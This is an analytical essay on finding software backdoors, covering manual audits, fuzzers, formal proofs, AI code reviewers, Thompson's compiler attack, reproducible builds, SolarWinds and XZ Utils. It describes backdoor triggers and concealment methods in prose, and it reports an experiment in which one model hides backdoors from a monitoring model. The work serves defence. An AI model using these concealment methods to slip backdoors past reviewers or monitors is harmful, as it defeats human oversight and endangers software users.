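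TrueCrypt was a free disk-encryption program whose developers never revealed their names. After the Snowden disclosures, its users raised money for an independent review. In April 2014, the security firm iSEC Partners reported 11 flaws in the Windows driver and start-up code but no evidence of a backdoor. A second team examined the encryption and reported four more problems in 2015, again with no signs of deliberate sabotage.

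In September 2015, James Forshaw of Google found two further vulnerabilities in the Windows driver, one of which could give an ordinary user full control of the computer. Nothing suggested that anyone had planted them, but they were in code that the first team had reviewed with backdoors in mind, so the team would presumably have missed a planted flaw of the same kind. The auditors had accurately reported that they found no evidence of a backdoor, but this did not mean that the driver was safe, as some readers may have assumed.

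### Lines per hour

Blaze and colleagues estimate that a trained engineer can inspect about 100 lines an hour under the best conditions. At that rate, reading Sequoia's 800,000 lines once takes 8,000 hours. The team thought this would have taken its eight members more than a year, which is about right if each can read attentively for a little under four hours a day.

Reading a network product with five million lines of code once would take 50,000 hours. A reviewer who reads for four hours a day on 220 days a year manages 880 hours, so the work would take one person about 57 years and a team of twenty almost three. If the vendor changes a tenth of the code each year, six more people have to read full-time to keep up. Britain's inspection of Huawei equipment faced a similar burden. These estimates don't include time for testing suspicions, or for a second reader to catch what the first one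 missed.

Inspectors therefore have to choose which code to read. If the code that handles logins, privileges and updates makes up 2% of the product, the team of twenty can read all 100,000 lines in under three weeks. This is a sensible use of their time only if the rest of the product cannot override that code. In many products it can, because all the code runs with the same privileges, and a buffer overflow in a minor feature, such as a status page, gives an attacker control of everything. Blaze complained that almost any bug in the voting systems could affect security, and concluded that they needed designs that stay secure even if reviewers miss some bugs.

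Developers can partly choose how much of their code is critical. Ka-Ping Yee, who was on the Sequoia team, kept that amount small in an experimental voting program called Pvote. The ballot's screens and sounds are prepared before the election, so the voting machine has to run only a few hundred lines of code. A reviewer can read that much in an afternoon, and several people can read it independently.

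Yee and David Wagner, who led the California review, used Pvote to study whether good programmers can find a deliberate flaw in such a short program. The blog Financial Cryptography (2013) later publicised an open challenge from Wagner to find the planted bug in a version he had reconstructed. Contestants knew that the bug existed. An inspector never knows this, and so has good reason to stop after reading a few hundred lines twice and finding nothing.

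A government can require the equipment it buys to have a small, isolated core. This may raise the probability of detection more than doubling the number of inspectors would, but it does not help with products already in use.

### Many eyes

Supporters of open-source software have a different answer to the shortage of readers. They publish the code so that anyone can look. *An empirical investigation of socio-technical code review metrics and security vulnerabilities* (Meneely, Neuberger and colleagues, 2014) quotes the writer Eric Raymond's version of the claim, "many eyes make all bugs shallow". The argument is that a bug which baffles one programmer will be obvious to another with different knowledge, so with enough readers somebody will see it.

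Borland's InterBase had a fixed login that went unnoticed for years and became public about half a year after Borland released the source in 2000. Publication clearly helped, but half a year is a long time to miss a plain-text password in a routine that checks passwords, and a disguised backdoor would have lasted longer. People were still finding serious security holes in Sendmail, a widely used mail program, after its source had been open to anyone for almost twenty years.

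Code that is open to inspection may go unread, and the people who do read it may not be looking for sabotage. Meneely and colleagues compared Chromium's review records with 667 vulnerabilities found after release. Files that more developers had reviewed were more likely to contain a vulnerability, even after allowing for file size. Files were less likely to contain one if their reviewers had previously helped to fix vulnerabilities. Difficult code probably attracts both reviewers and flaws, so the first result doesn't show that extra reviewers cause flaws. But it counts against using the number of readers as a measure of safety, and the second result suggests that an inspector should check whether the reviewers had experience fixing vulnerabilities.

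Extra readers help most if each has a fair chance of finding the flaw and they miss different things. If two pairs each have an independent 80% chance, both will find the flaw 64% of the time and at least one will find it 96% of the time, which is close to the Rice results. If a subtler backdoor gives each team only a 20% chance, it takes ten independent teams to have about a 90% chance that at least one finds it. Real teams are not fully independent, because they learn from the same guides and look first in the same places. A developer who knows those guides can put the backdoor where all ten teams are likely to miss it.

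## What automated tools and AI reviewers can find

Reading speed limits human reviewers, but an automated tool can search five million lines of source code in minutes. The harder task is recognising a backdoor. Some tools look for suspicious patterns in the code, and others run the program on huge numbers of inputs. For small programs, a mathematical proof can rule out whole classes of misbehaviour. Researchers have also planted backdoors to test AI models as reviewers.

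### Searching the code for warning signs

Static analysis tools search source code or a binary for a set of patterns, without running the code, and list places for a person to check. Wysopal and Eng describe patterns for four classes of backdoor: special credentials such as a fixed password, hidden functions such as an undocumented command, unexpected network activity, and tampering with values that control security, as in the Linux attempt.

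To find special credentials, the tool collects every fixed piece of text in the program and keeps those that could be secrets. For example, a string of 32 or 40 characters, all digits or letters from a to f, may be a password hash, the scrambled form in which programs store passwords. The tool also looks for fixed data that the program passes to an encryption routine. This second check would have exposed the Interbase login, because the program passed a fixed password to its own scrambling function.

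In a web application, the tool can list every parameter the server accepts and remove those that appear in the forms on the application's pages, which leaves the inputs that ordinary visitors never send. The backdoor in WordPress used two of these, called "ix" and "iz". The tool also lists every place where the program opens a network connection and picks out fixed addresses and port numbers. In 2002 somebody altered tcpdump, a program that displays network traffic, so that it hid all traffic on port 1963. A second program, installed during the build, used that port to receive the intruder's commands.

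Harmless code matches these patterns too. Many products contact a fixed address to check for updates, and C programmers often change a value inside a condition on purpose. Wysopal and Eng therefore expect many false alarms and want a person to review the results. They cite a 2007 study that checked 100 randomly chosen software packages with detection tools and manual analysis and reported unwanted code, such as backdoors, in 23 of them. "Unwanted code" is a broad category, so the study is weak evidence about how common backdoors are.

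*ROSA* later tested its own fuzzing tool against Stringer, a static tool that searches binaries for suspicious fixed text, on 17 programs with known backdoors. Stringer was faster but found only four of the backdoors and raised 44 times as many false alarms. Pattern searches like Stringer's are fast enough to run on every product, but a clean result is weak evidence that a product has no backdoor.

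### Why no tool can decide every case

Better patterns would help, but no tool can give a correct yes or no answer for every possible program. This follows from a theorem Henry Gordon Rice published in 1953, which covers any question about what a program does, rather than how its text looks, unless the answer is the same for all programs.

A perfect backdoor detector cannot exist, because it could be used to work out whether a program ever finishes, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can do this for every program. For any harmless program P, someone could write a router login that runs P and, once P finishes, accepts the password "k7Vw2mQz" from anyone. This backdoor works only if P finishes, so a perfect detector would reveal whether it does.

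Every real tool must therefore sometimes miss a backdoor, raise a false alarm or give no answer. This limit matters less in practice because an inspector has to judge only one product, not all possible programs. If the tool can't clear a piece of code, the inspector can ask the vendor to rewrite it more simply. That is reasonable for the code that controls logins and updates, but expensive for a whole product.

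### Running the program and watching its system calls

Wysopal and Eng thought it impossible to find most backdoors by running the program, because the tester does not know the secret input. Fuzzers have since become much better at finding such inputs. A modern fuzzer starts with a few sample inputs, alters them at random and runs the program on each altered input. If one reaches code that no earlier input reached, the fuzzer keeps it and alters it further.

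Some fuzzers can also split a comparison with a fixed password into one comparison per character, so that each correct character counts as progress. In the ideal case, finding an eight-character password of letters and digits takes at most 62 guesses per position, or 496 in all, whereas guessing the whole password at once could take 218 trillion.

The fuzzer also needs a sign that it has triggered the backdoor. Ordinary fuzzers look for crashes, which works for buffer overflows, but a well-made backdoor doesn't crash. ROSA uses system calls instead. These are the requests a program makes to the operating system when it wants to read a file, open a network connection or start another program, and a backdoor that affects anything outside its own program has to make some. The method has four steps:

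1. ROSA fuzzes the program for about a minute and stores the resulting inputs as examples of normal behaviour. A fuzzer is unlikely to hit a backdoor in so short a time.
2. It continues fuzzing for hours. For each new input, it looks up the stored input that took the most similar path through the code.
3. It compares the types of system call that the program made on the two inputs, and reports any difference.
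4. A person examines each report and decides whether the behaviour is legitimate.

*ROSA* illustrates this with sudo, a command that lets authorised users run programs under another account. A planted master password, "let_me_in", takes almost the same path through the code as a wrong password, but it starts a new program instead of producing an error message. In the real backdoor in the file server ProFTPD, the extra calls switched to the root account and opened a command shell. A reviewer can quickly confirm or dismiss a report like this.

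ROSA's developers tested it on 17 backdoors, seven of them real. A researcher who had not worked on the tool planted most of the others, and the developers searched for those without knowing how they worked. ROSA found every backdoor in at least one run and succeeded in 156 of 180 runs, each lasting up to eight hours. It took an hour and a half on average, and a person had to check about seven suspicious behaviours per run.

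These are good results, but ROSA only runs programs built for Linux on ordinary PC processors. The researchers had to adapt several router programs before testing them and gave up on software from two other devices because it depended on missing libraries and hardware. An inspector who has the source code can often build a version for a PC, but parts of a network product may not work without its special chips.

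### Comparing a new version with the old one

A project that accepts changes every day can't spend eight hours and a person's attention on each one. Lily, the change-vetting tool from Kokkonis and colleagues, fuzzes each new version for ten minutes. It first runs the new version on inputs kept from earlier fuzzing and records which combinations of system calls occur. It then fuzzes the new version and reports an input only if the input produces a combination that is not in the record and that the previous version does not produce when given the same input.

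For example, while fuzzing the doctored vsFTPd release, Lily eventually tries a username containing ":)". The program then opens a network port and starts a command shell, a combination of calls that none of the recorded inputs produces. The previous, clean release doesn't do this with the same username, so Lily reports a backdoor. It then identifies which of the changed lines ran on this input and which of those led to the unusual calls. This narrows the 1,407 lines that differ across five files to seven lines in one file. Anyone who knows C can see from those seven lines that the server offers a shell to whoever connects.

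Kokkonis and colleagues tested Lily on 13 open-source programs, using backdoors from the ROSA benchmark. They ran it 20 times on each change, testing both single commits (individual changes to the source code) and whole releases, which can contain years of changes. They also measured how many false alarms Lily would raise using only one of its two conditions.

| | Commits | Releases |
|---|---|---|
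| Safe changes tested | 432 | 50 |
| Backdoored changes tested | 13 | 50 |
| Average detection rate | 90% | 83% |
| False alarms | 0.2% | 4.3% |
| False alarms if Lily reports everything new | 10% | 58% |
| False alarms if Lily reports everything unusual | 14% | 20% |

The detection rates are averages over single ten-minute runs, and every backdoor was found in at least one of its 20 runs. Only 39% of runs on releases of the image library libpng succeeded, because the code connecting the fuzzer to the older versions was still immature. If runs are independent, five of them would raise the chance of detection from 39% to about 92%. Repetition does little about false alarms, because 40 of the 43 on releases came from two updates of one sound library, which triggered false alarms in every run.

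Whether a false-alarm rate is tolerable depends on how rare backdoors are. If one change in a thousand contained a backdoor, then at the rates in the table, about one in three of Lily's alarms on commits would be real, but only about one in fifty on releases. Even that many false alarms would be manageable, because each report in the release tests pointed to a dozen lines or fewer.

Lily misses backdoors that were there from the start, and it also can't detect those in code that the fuzzer never runs. In 337 code changes that Kokkonis and colleagues examined, fuzzing covered about 32% of the code on average. They acknowledge that an attacker who studies the tool might evade it, though with considerable effort and no guarantee of success. The method also depends on a visible change in system calls. The replaced constant in Juniper's firewalls caused no such change, so neither ROSA nor Lily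 would have reported it.

### What a proof rules out

Even a long fuzzing run tries only a small share of the possible inputs, whereas formal verification covers all of them with a mathematical proof. Specialists prove that the code meets a specification, which states precisely what the program should do, and a small, well-tested program checks every step of the proof. If the code doesn't meet the specification, the specialists reach a step they can't prove, which usually leads them to the error. Rice's theorem doesn't rule this out, because people supply the proof for one particular program.

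The best-known example is seL4, a microkernel (the small core of an operating system that controls which programs may use which memory and devices). In 2009 a team at NICTA, an Australian research centre, completed a proof that the kernel's roughly 8,700 lines of C code behave as specified on every input. This rules out buffer overflows and use-after-free errors, including deliberate ones.

Later proofs showed that the kernel enforces its access rules, so a program cannot read or change another program's memory without permission. For some processors, researchers also proved that the binary matches the C code, which removes the need to trust the compiler. The proofs assume that the hardware works as documented and that certain start-up and machine-level code is correct. The proof about reading memory also doesn't cover timing, and one program can sometimes learn another's secrets from how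 long an operation takes.

A proof rules out only what the specification forbids. Suppose the specification for the router's login program reads, "Anyone who enters a valid name and password gets a session." The version with the secret password meets this specification because valid users still get in. The specification also has to state that nobody else gets a session. Even then, the proof will succeed if the specification lists a hidden maintenance account among the valid ones. Likewise, a random number generator could be proven to follow the Dual_EC_DRBG standard and still have the weakness in the standard's constants.

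The inspector therefore has to read the specification as suspiciously as they would read source code. This is still worthwhile, because a specification is usually shorter and leaves out the details where bugdoors hide. The inspector can also rerun the proof checker on their own computer instead of trusting the vendor's claim that the proof is complete.

The main obstacle to verification is the labor it takes. The proof specific to seL4 took about 11 person-years. At the same rate per line, a five-million-line network product would need more than 6,000. Verification is realistic for a small core that confines the rest of the product. If the router runs on such a core, a backdoor in its status page can't take over the login program. A backdoor in the login program would still work, because that program is allowed to open sessions.

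### AI reviewers against planted backdoors

A language model, an AI system trained on large amounts of text and code, can read a program and explain what it appears to do. The reviewer gives the model the code, asks it to look for backdoors, and gets back a written list of findings. Many current systems also let the model search files and run other tools. These abilities make AI review more flexible than a pattern search, but the model can report a problem that does not exist or dismiss a real one because of a weak justification.

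In an experiment from *Scaling Laws For Scalable Oversight* (Engels, Baek and colleagues, 2025), one model inserted a backdoor into a short Python program from a set of competition problems, and a second model reviewed the code with the comments removed. The first model won if the program passed its original tests, gave a wrong answer on an input that the first model had chosen, and did not arouse the reviewer's suspicion.

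From the results, the researchers gave each model separate ratings as hider and reviewer, using the Elo system familiar from chess. If the hider's rating is *H* and the reviewer's is *G*, the reviewer's chance of winning is

1 / (1 + 10^((*H* − *G*)/400)).

Engels and colleagues then compared these ratings with each model's general ability, as measured by Chatbot Arena, a public ranking of language models. Both ratings rose with general ability, but the hider's rose faster. Using a mathematical model based on these trends, they calculated that review would succeed only 10.0% of the time if the hider was 400 points stronger in general ability, even with a chain of reviewers in which a weaker trusted model checks a somewhat stronger one, which then checks the next.

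The 10.0% is not a measured detection rate. In the games, even the strongest hiders barely won half the time against the weakest reviewers. Stronger hiders did better mainly because their backdoors worked more often; their working backdoors were no more likely to get past the reviewer. A vendor's programmers can already write working code, so an inspector can learn little about them from this advantage. The backdoors were also often obvious to people. The experiment suggests that reviewers do worse if hiders improve faster than they do, but it is weak evidence for any particular detection rate in a real product.

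In *PRWeaver*, Wang, Cheng and Xie (2026) planted 208 attacks in ten real open-source projects, most of them web software written in Python, and ran each attack to confirm that it worked. The attacks weakened access rules, logins, payments and other protections. The researchers then tested six combinations of review tool and language model, counting an attack as found only if the tool's report identified the planted weakness.

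When the whole attack arrived as one change, the reviewers found between 42% and 79% of attacks. The best combination of model and tool did about as well as a pair of Rice students had done on a far smaller program. The tool mattered as well as the model. Claude Haiku 4.5, a small model, found 56% of the attacks with one tool and 67% with another. Wang and colleagues report no false-alarm rate, so it is unclear how many harmless findings a person would have had to read.

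Reviewers found far more attacks when they examined less code at a time. In one comparison, the attack was spread among 24 harmless changes. Reviewers that examined the changes one by one found 50–60% of the attacks, while those that received them all together found only 16–22%. An inspector who pastes a whole release into a model will therefore probably miss backdoors that the model could have found in smaller pieces of code.

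In some failures, the AI reviewer found the relevant code but misjudged it. In one case, two changes to a "trust this browser" feature let a stolen login remain valid after the user reset the password. The reviewer described both changes correctly but did not flag them, because it treated them as deliberate trade-offs between security and convenience.

### AI reviewers without source code

Binaries are harder to read than source code because they lack the original names and structure. In *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries*, Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) planted backdoors in four open-source network programs and gave AI models only the binaries. The models could use reverse-engineering tools such as Ghidra, which translates machine instructions back into rough C code. In most tasks, a model had to state that there was a backdoor and give the address of the function containing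 it.

The best model, Claude Opus 4.6, succeeded in 49% of the tasks. Grabowski and colleagues had not tried hard to disguise the backdoors and thought a skilled human could find them fairly easily. On clean binaries, the models reported nonexistent problems 28% of the time. The researchers would want a rate below 0.001% for practical use.

In one case, a model found a backdoor in a web server in five minutes. It listed the functions that the server imported from the operating system and identified one that runs shell commands. It traced the call back to the code that handled a "debug" header in web requests, and found that this code executed whatever text the header contained.

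In another program, dnsmasq, which assigns network addresses to devices, Claude Opus 4.6 found the planted code and saw that it started a command shell. It concluded this was probably a normal feature, since dnsmasq does run scripts, but never checked where the command came from. The command arrived in a network packet, so anyone who could send such a packet could control the machine.

The average false-alarm rate hides large differences between models. Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?*, which ranks models on the same benchmark, gives Gemini 3.1 Pro a detection rate of 49% with 17% false alarms. A version of GPT-5.2 Codex set to reason at length detected 46% with no false alarms, but the benchmark has only 33 tasks, so this shows only that its false-alarm rate is low. The best score rose from 21% for a model released in March 2025 to 49% for one released eleven months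 later.

AI reviewers, like Lily, benefit from having a previous version to compare against. In *Binary Diff Summarization using Large Language Models* (2025), Udeshi, Putrevu and colleagues planted three kinds of malware in updates to six open-source projects. Their system used Ghidra to find the functions that differed between the old and new binaries. A language model summarised each of these functions and scored it for sensitive behaviour, such as opening network connections or reading passwords. The model then judged from the highest-scoring functions whether the update was malicious.

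With GPT-5 mini, the system caught 64% of the infected updates, and 98% of its alarms were correct. The 98% figure overstates how reliable its alarms would be in practice, because three-quarters of the updates in the test were infected. The published numbers imply that the system raised a false alarm on about 4% of the 98 clean updates. If only one update in a thousand were infected, roughly one alarm in sixty would be real, which is similar to Lily's performance on releases.

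The planted malware was conspicuous and included ransomware. But Udeshi and colleagues also tried the system on the real XZ Utils backdoor, and it gave the malicious functions high scores. *ROSA*'s benchmark had left out this backdoor because a fuzzer can't produce its trigger in a reasonable time. A language model reads the code, so it doesn't need the trigger, although in this case it may also have learned from published accounts of the attack.

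### From finding errors to finding concealment

In April 2026 the AI company Anthropic announced that its model Claude Mythos Preview had found thousands of previously unknown vulnerabilities, including some in every major operating system and web browser. Through Project Glasswing, the company gave selected companies and open-source developers early access to the model so they could fix their software before similar models became widely available.

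*Assessing Claude Mythos Preview’s cybersecurity capabilities* (Carlini, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) describes a simple search method. The model first rates every file from 1 to 5 by how likely it is to contain interesting flaws. Separate copies of the model then each read one file, look for possible flaws and run the program to test them. A final copy checks whether each reported flaw is real and serious.

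A thousand such runs on OpenBSD, an operating system known for its security, cost less than $20,000. They found a 27-year-old flaw that let an attacker crash a machine over the network, along with several dozen other findings. In FFmpeg, a widely used video library, the model found a flaw that fuzzers and human reviewers had missed for 16 years. FFmpeg numbers the slices of each video frame and uses 65,535 to mark a position that belongs to no slice. If a frame has enough slices, a real slice gets that number, and FFmpeg writes outside its memory.

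It is less certain how much of this was new. Epoch AI's *Are Mythos’ cyber capabilities overhyped?* (2026) distinguishes finding flaws from exploiting them. Mythos Preview was about seven months ahead of the trend in exploitation, but the evidence on finding flaws was mixed. At 21 organisations, the number of serious vulnerabilities in May 2026 exceeded the 2025 baseline by 262%, but Project Glasswing had also sharply increased spending on the search. In curl, a heavily audited program for transferring data, the model found one minor vulnerability and reported four that weren't real. Earlier AI tools had apparently already found most of curl's vulnerabilities.

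Epoch AI sees a clearer gain in the quality of Mythos Preview's reports. The model raises fewer false alarms, partly because it can write a working attack to confirm that a flaw is real. For an inspection team with too few experts, fewer false alarms may matter as much as finding more flaws.

These skills should carry over well to backdoors disguised as mistakes, or bugdoors, because a model that finds accidental buffer overflows will also find deliberate ones. A model can also look through an entire product, including the minor features that human inspectors don't have time to read, so a developer can no longer count on a bugdoor staying hidden in one of them.

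There is less reason to be confident about finding backdoors that contain no error. Carlini and colleagues concentrated on memory errors partly because these are easy to confirm. The tool AddressSanitizer stops a program when it misuses memory, so a model can test many ideas and reliably learn which are right. With this kind of check, all 112 Firefox bugs that Claude Opus 4.6 reported were real. No comparable tool can confirm that a maintenance login is illegitimate, because the program runs exactly as written. Claude Opus 4.6 examined the backdoor in dnsmasq but gave an innocent explanation for it.

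None of these planted-backdoor tests included Mythos Preview or a similarly capable model. A stronger model would probably trace the command in dnsmasq back to the network packet. It might do no better with the "trust this browser" changes, because the reviewer had already interpreted the code correctly but lacked information about what the product was supposed to allow. That information is in design documents and promises to customers, so a model given only the source code has to guess.

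Inspectors can reduce the guesswork by giving the model the product's documentation and having it list every input that leads to a privileged action, along with the documented reason for allowing it. A person then checks any entry whose reason is missing or weak. For dnsmasq, a complete list would have included a network packet whose contents the program runs as a command.

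## Proving that the inspected code is the code that runs

Even if reviewers and tools miss nothing in the source code, the vendor, or an intruder on the vendor's build machines, can still put a backdoor into the binary. The inspector can bypass those machines by compiling the source and installing the result on the router, but then depends on a compiler, which is itself a binary that somebody else built.

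### A compiler that hides its own backdoor

Paul Karger and Roger Schell described this problem in June 1974, in a security review of the Multics operating system for the US Air Force. According to research!rsc's *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler* (2023), the review suggested requiring source code so that buyers could inspect a system on delivery, and it named a backdoored compiler as a possible obstacle. The Multics compiler for the language PL/I was itself written in PL/I, so an older version compiled each new one. A backdoor in the compiler could therefore "maintain itself, even when the compiler is recompiled" (quoted in Wheeler's *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, 2009).

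Thompson (1984), in *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, explained how to build such a compiler for Unix, the operating system he had helped to create. The attack has three stages:

1. The attacker changes the compiler's source so that the compiler recognises the login program and adds code that accepts a secret password. The login program's source stays clean, but anyone who reads the compiler's source can see the change.
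2. The attacker adds a second change, which makes the compiler recognise its own source and insert both changes into the new compiler. The inserted code has to reproduce its own text, which programmers know how to arrange.
3. The attacker compiles this source once, installs the resulting binary and restores the original source.

The source of both programs is now clean, but the installed compiler still adds the backdoor when it compiles the login program, and both changes when it compiles the compiler's own source. Recompiling everything from clean source therefore does not remove the backdoor.

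Thompson used a harmless example to show how a binary can carry something that its source lacks. C programmers write `\n` for the newline character, which the compiler must translate into the number 10. The source of the first compiler to support `\n` must contain the 10. Once that compiler is installed, its programmer can replace the 10 in the source with `\n`, because the installed binary already translates `\n` correctly. Each compiler binary then puts the 10 into the next one it compiles, although the source no longer contains it.

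In 2023 Thompson supplied his original code to research!rsc, where it was run on a simulated Unix of the period. The code consists of 99 lines of C and a 20-line script, and file dates show that he had finished it by June 1975. The infected compiler was 12,918 bytes, compared with 10,724 for the clean one. The secret password still opened the administrator's account after the compiler and the login program were rebuilt from clean source.

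Thompson had tricked another group at Bell Labs into installing the compiler, and accounts differ on what happened next. Wheeler writes that nobody ever detected the attack. In most retellings collected by research!rsc, the group noticed that the compiler grew each time it compiled itself, because of a bug in Thompson's code, and eventually got back to a clean version. Thompson said in 2023 that the group broke the backdoor without finding out what it was. Nobody in any of these versions found it by reading source code. Reading the binary would also have been difficult, because Thompson had altered the disassembler, the tool that displays a binary's instructions, to hide the additions.

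### Compiling the compiler twice

Henry Spencer outlined a defence in a short internet posting in 1998. Wheeler worked it out in detail, named it diverse double-compiling and tested it. The inspector needs the source of the suspect compiler and a second compiler from an unrelated maker. Call the suspect compiler A, its source *s* and the second compiler T. In the simplest case, A is supposed to be the result of compiling *s* with a compiler built from the same source. The inspector then works as follows:

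1. Compile *s* with A. The result should be identical to A. If it isn't, the inspector probably has the wrong source, settings or tools and has to sort this out first.
2. Compile *s* with T. The result, called stage 1, should behave like A, but its bits differ because T translates C in its own way.
3. Compile *s* again, this time with stage 1. The result is stage 2.
4. Compare stage 2 with A, bit for bit.

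If *c*(*s*, X) stands for the binary that compiler X makes from source *s*, the test is whether

*c*(*s*, *c*(*s*, T)) = A.

The method relies on two correct translations of one program behaving alike. It does not require different compilers to produce the same binary, which would almost never happen. If two compilers translate a program that adds 2 and 2, the binaries differ but both print 4. Here the program is a compiler and its output is another binary. Stage 1 and a clean A both translate C in the way that *s* prescribes, so they must produce the same output from the same input. If A contains Thompson's backdoor, the first step still succeeds, because A adds the backdoor to the new copy. But stage 1 came from T, which adds nothing, so stage 2 lacks the backdoor and the final comparison fails.

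When a different compiler built A, such as an older version of A, the inspector compiles that parent compiler's source in the first round and A's source in the second, and has to review both sources.

Wheeler formally proves that, under several assumptions, a match shows that A corresponds to its source. T must not contain a backdoor that affects this compilation, although it may be slow, lack most features or even have backdoors aimed at other programs. T must also interpret the language as the source requires. The computers that run the test and the program that compares the results must be trustworthy. For an honest compiler to pass, its output must not vary from run to run.

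To defeat the test, an attacker would have to plant the same backdoor in T, either by guessing which compiler the inspector will choose or by subverting all the likely ones. The inspector can repeat the test with several compilers, or write a simple one and keep it secret. Wheeler points out that the defender has the advantage here, which is unusual in computer security.

A can match and still contain a backdoor, because any bugdoor in *s* is also in A, so somebody still has to read *s*. A mismatch shows only that one of the assumptions failed, and the cause may be innocent. In Wheeler's first demonstration, which used a small C compiler called tcc, the binaries differed at first because of two bugs. One made tcc choose longer instructions than necessary, and the other left unpredictable values in two unused bytes of output. The binaries matched once Wheeler had worked around both bugs.

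A second demonstration used two Lisp compilers by Wolfgang Goerigk, one clean and one with a Thompson-style backdoor. Both could reproduce themselves from the clean source, so the first step alone could not distinguish them. The output of diverse double-compiling matched the clean compiler but not the backdoored one. The differing lines included code that checked for a login program, which no compiler needs to do.

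The third test used GCC, the standard compiler on most Linux systems. Wheeler could not regenerate the copy that came with the Fedora distribution because Fedora had not recorded enough about how it built the compiler. He therefore built a new copy of GCC and checked it with Intel's compiler as T. The results differed at first because GCC's build process reused one library from an earlier round instead of recompiling it. After he corrected this, every bit matched. The test shows that the method works on a large industrial compiler, but not that the copies of GCC in general use were clean.

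A language's designers can also avoid the problem. Each version of the compiler for Google's Go language is built with an earlier released version, back to version 1.4, which is written in C. As research!rsc explains, anyone can repeat the whole chain, and the compiler never has to compile itself. The chain still starts with a C compiler, which must be checked separately.

### Builds that give the same result twice

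Every comparison of this kind, whether of a compiler or of a router's login program, depends on a reproducible build, but most builds pick up details of their surroundings. Many tools write the current date and time into the binary. Others record the name of the folder or the user. Some process files in the order the disk lists them, which varies between machines. In *reproduce.debian.net*, a talk to developers of the Linux distribution Debian, Levsen (2026) lists the common causes of differences between builds as "timestamps, timestamps, timestamps", then build paths, then all the rest, and adds that there might be backdoors among them.

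The repairs are mostly simple. Programmers can replace the current time with the date of the last change to the source, sort the lists of files and leave out folder names. They build a program twice under deliberately different conditions to find the remaining causes. Reproducible Builds (2026), a monthly report from the project that coordinates this work, describes disorderfs, a tool for this purpose that makes a computer's file system behave unpredictably.

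Once a build is reproducible, people who don't trust the distributor can check it. When Debian builds a package, it saves a file that lists the versions of the compiler and other tools it used. An independent server, called a rebuilder, recreates that environment, builds the package from source and compares the result with the one on Debian's download site. Rebuilders can publish their results as cryptographic hashes. A hash is a short number calculated from a file, and in practice any change to the file changes the hash. If several rebuilders run by different people get the same hash as Debian, an attacker could have tampered with the build only by compromising all of them or something they share. They all use the same compiler binary, so a Thompson-style backdoor in it would pass this check.

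Levsen counted five or six rebuilders for Debian and urged the audience to set up more, asking "do you really want to put all your trust in me". Trixie is Debian's stable release, and forky is the next one, still in preparation. The results in May 2026 were as follows:

| Packages | Reproduced | Source packages that failed |
|---|---|---|
| Forky, for ordinary PCs | 97.2% | 512 |
| Forky, for any processor | 98.3% | 419 |
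| Trixie, for ordinary PCs | 95.6% | 803 |
| Trixie, for any processor | 91.7% | 2,001 |
| Trixie security updates, for ordinary PCs | 82.7% | 15 |

The first mass rebuild, in September 2013, reproduced only 24% of Debian's packages, according to Nesbitt's *reproducible builds in language package managers* (2026). That figure is only roughly comparable with later ones because the testing method has changed. Reproducible Builds' results page shows that 95.4% of forky's PC packages currently pass a separate stress test, which deliberately varies the build conditions. The figures in the table are more relevant to someone deciding whether to trust a download, because they concern the files that users install.

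In May, Gevers (2026) announced in *bits from the release team* that "Debian must ship reproducible packages". Debian's software now keeps a new package out of the next release if nobody can reproduce it. It also blocks a new version of an existing package if earlier versions could be reproduced but the new one can't. Maintainers can ask for exceptions, and older packages that have never been reproducible may stay for now. Those older packages are the best place for an intruder on Debian's build machines to hide a backdoor, because nobody is surprised when a rebuilt copy doesn't match Debian's.

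Other collections of software are much further behind. In *No Snake Oil*, which Reproducible Builds summarises, Dietrich, Sun and colleagues studied 12,180 popular releases from PyPI, the main public collection of Python packages. Two automated rebuilding tools produced identical files in 15.4% and 19.1% of their rebuilds. A program that ignores differences it can show to be harmless accepted 60.2% and 78.9% of the rebuilds that started from equivalent source. Anyone can check that two files are identical, but an inspector who uses such a program has to trust its rules about which differences are harmless.

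Builds can also stop being reproducible over time. Nanni, Malka and colleagues tried to rebuild 18,904 versions of Android apps that the app store F-Droid had once reproduced. They could still build 83% of them, and 94% of those came out identical, or 78% overall. Missing dependencies caused most of the failures, so an inspector should keep copies of the compiler, libraries and settings as well as the source. Even an honest build may not match if a distributor processes the file before delivery. Reproducible Builds (2025) reported that Google's Play Store had broken reproducible builds for the messaging app Signal.

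Only the vendor and the inspectors can attempt to rebuild a commercial product, because nobody else has the source. If the build isn't reproducible, they have to establish binary equivalence by explaining every difference between the rebuilt and shipped binaries. Britain's inspectors of Huawei equipment spent years on this.

### SolarWinds and the infected build machine

SolarWinds, an American company, sells Orion, a program that organisations use to monitor their networks. In September 2019 intruders got into the company's systems. The US government later identified them as Russia's foreign intelligence service. The intruders first practised by adding harmless code to Orion, and nobody noticed. In February 2020 they put a malicious program, later named SUNSPOT by the security company CrowdStrike, on the build machines.

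When a build of Orion began, SUNSPOT replaced one source file with a backdoored version, then restored the original when the compiler finished. Before the swap, it checked the original file's hash, because a backdoored copy of an outdated file might have made the build fail and attracted attention. It also suppressed compiler warnings about the added code.

SolarWinds signed the infected binary and began distributing it as a normal update in March 2020. The company estimated that fewer than 18,000 customers installed it. The intruders then broke into far fewer of them, including nine US federal agencies. The backdoor stayed inactive for up to two weeks after installation, so a short test would have missed it. In December 2020 the security company FireEye discovered it while investigating a theft of its own hacking tools.

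The backdoor was never in Orion's stored source code, so an inspector could have read all of that code without finding it. Checking the signature would not have helped, because SolarWinds itself had signed the file. A rebuild on a clean, separate machine would have produced a different binary, but someone would still have had to tell the backdoor apart from any harmless differences, which is easy only if the build is reproducible. SolarWinds later began to build its software in several separate environments and compare the results. This protects customers against an intruder who controls one environment, but a vendor that controls all of them could still insert a backdoor.

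### XZ Utils and the altered release package

XZ Utils is a set of free compression tools that comes with almost every Linux system. For years, one unpaid volunteer, Lasse Collin, did most of the work on it. An attacker using the name Jia Tan spent more than two years gaining control:

- **October 2021:** Jia Tan sends a first small, harmless patch. Many useful ones follow.
- **April to June 2022:** People whom nobody in the project knows complain about slow progress and press Collin to share the work. Collin mentions long-term mental health problems and says that Jia Tan may take on a bigger role.
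- **Early 2023:** Jia Tan begins to change the project's repository directly and, in March, to publish releases.
- **February 2024:** Jia Tan adds test files that contain a disguised backdoor and releases version 5.6.0 a day later.
- **March 2024:** An improved version, 5.6.1, follows on 9 March. Andres Freund exposes the backdoor on 29 March.

The other accounts that pressed Collin were probably part of the attack, although nobody has established who was behind any of them.

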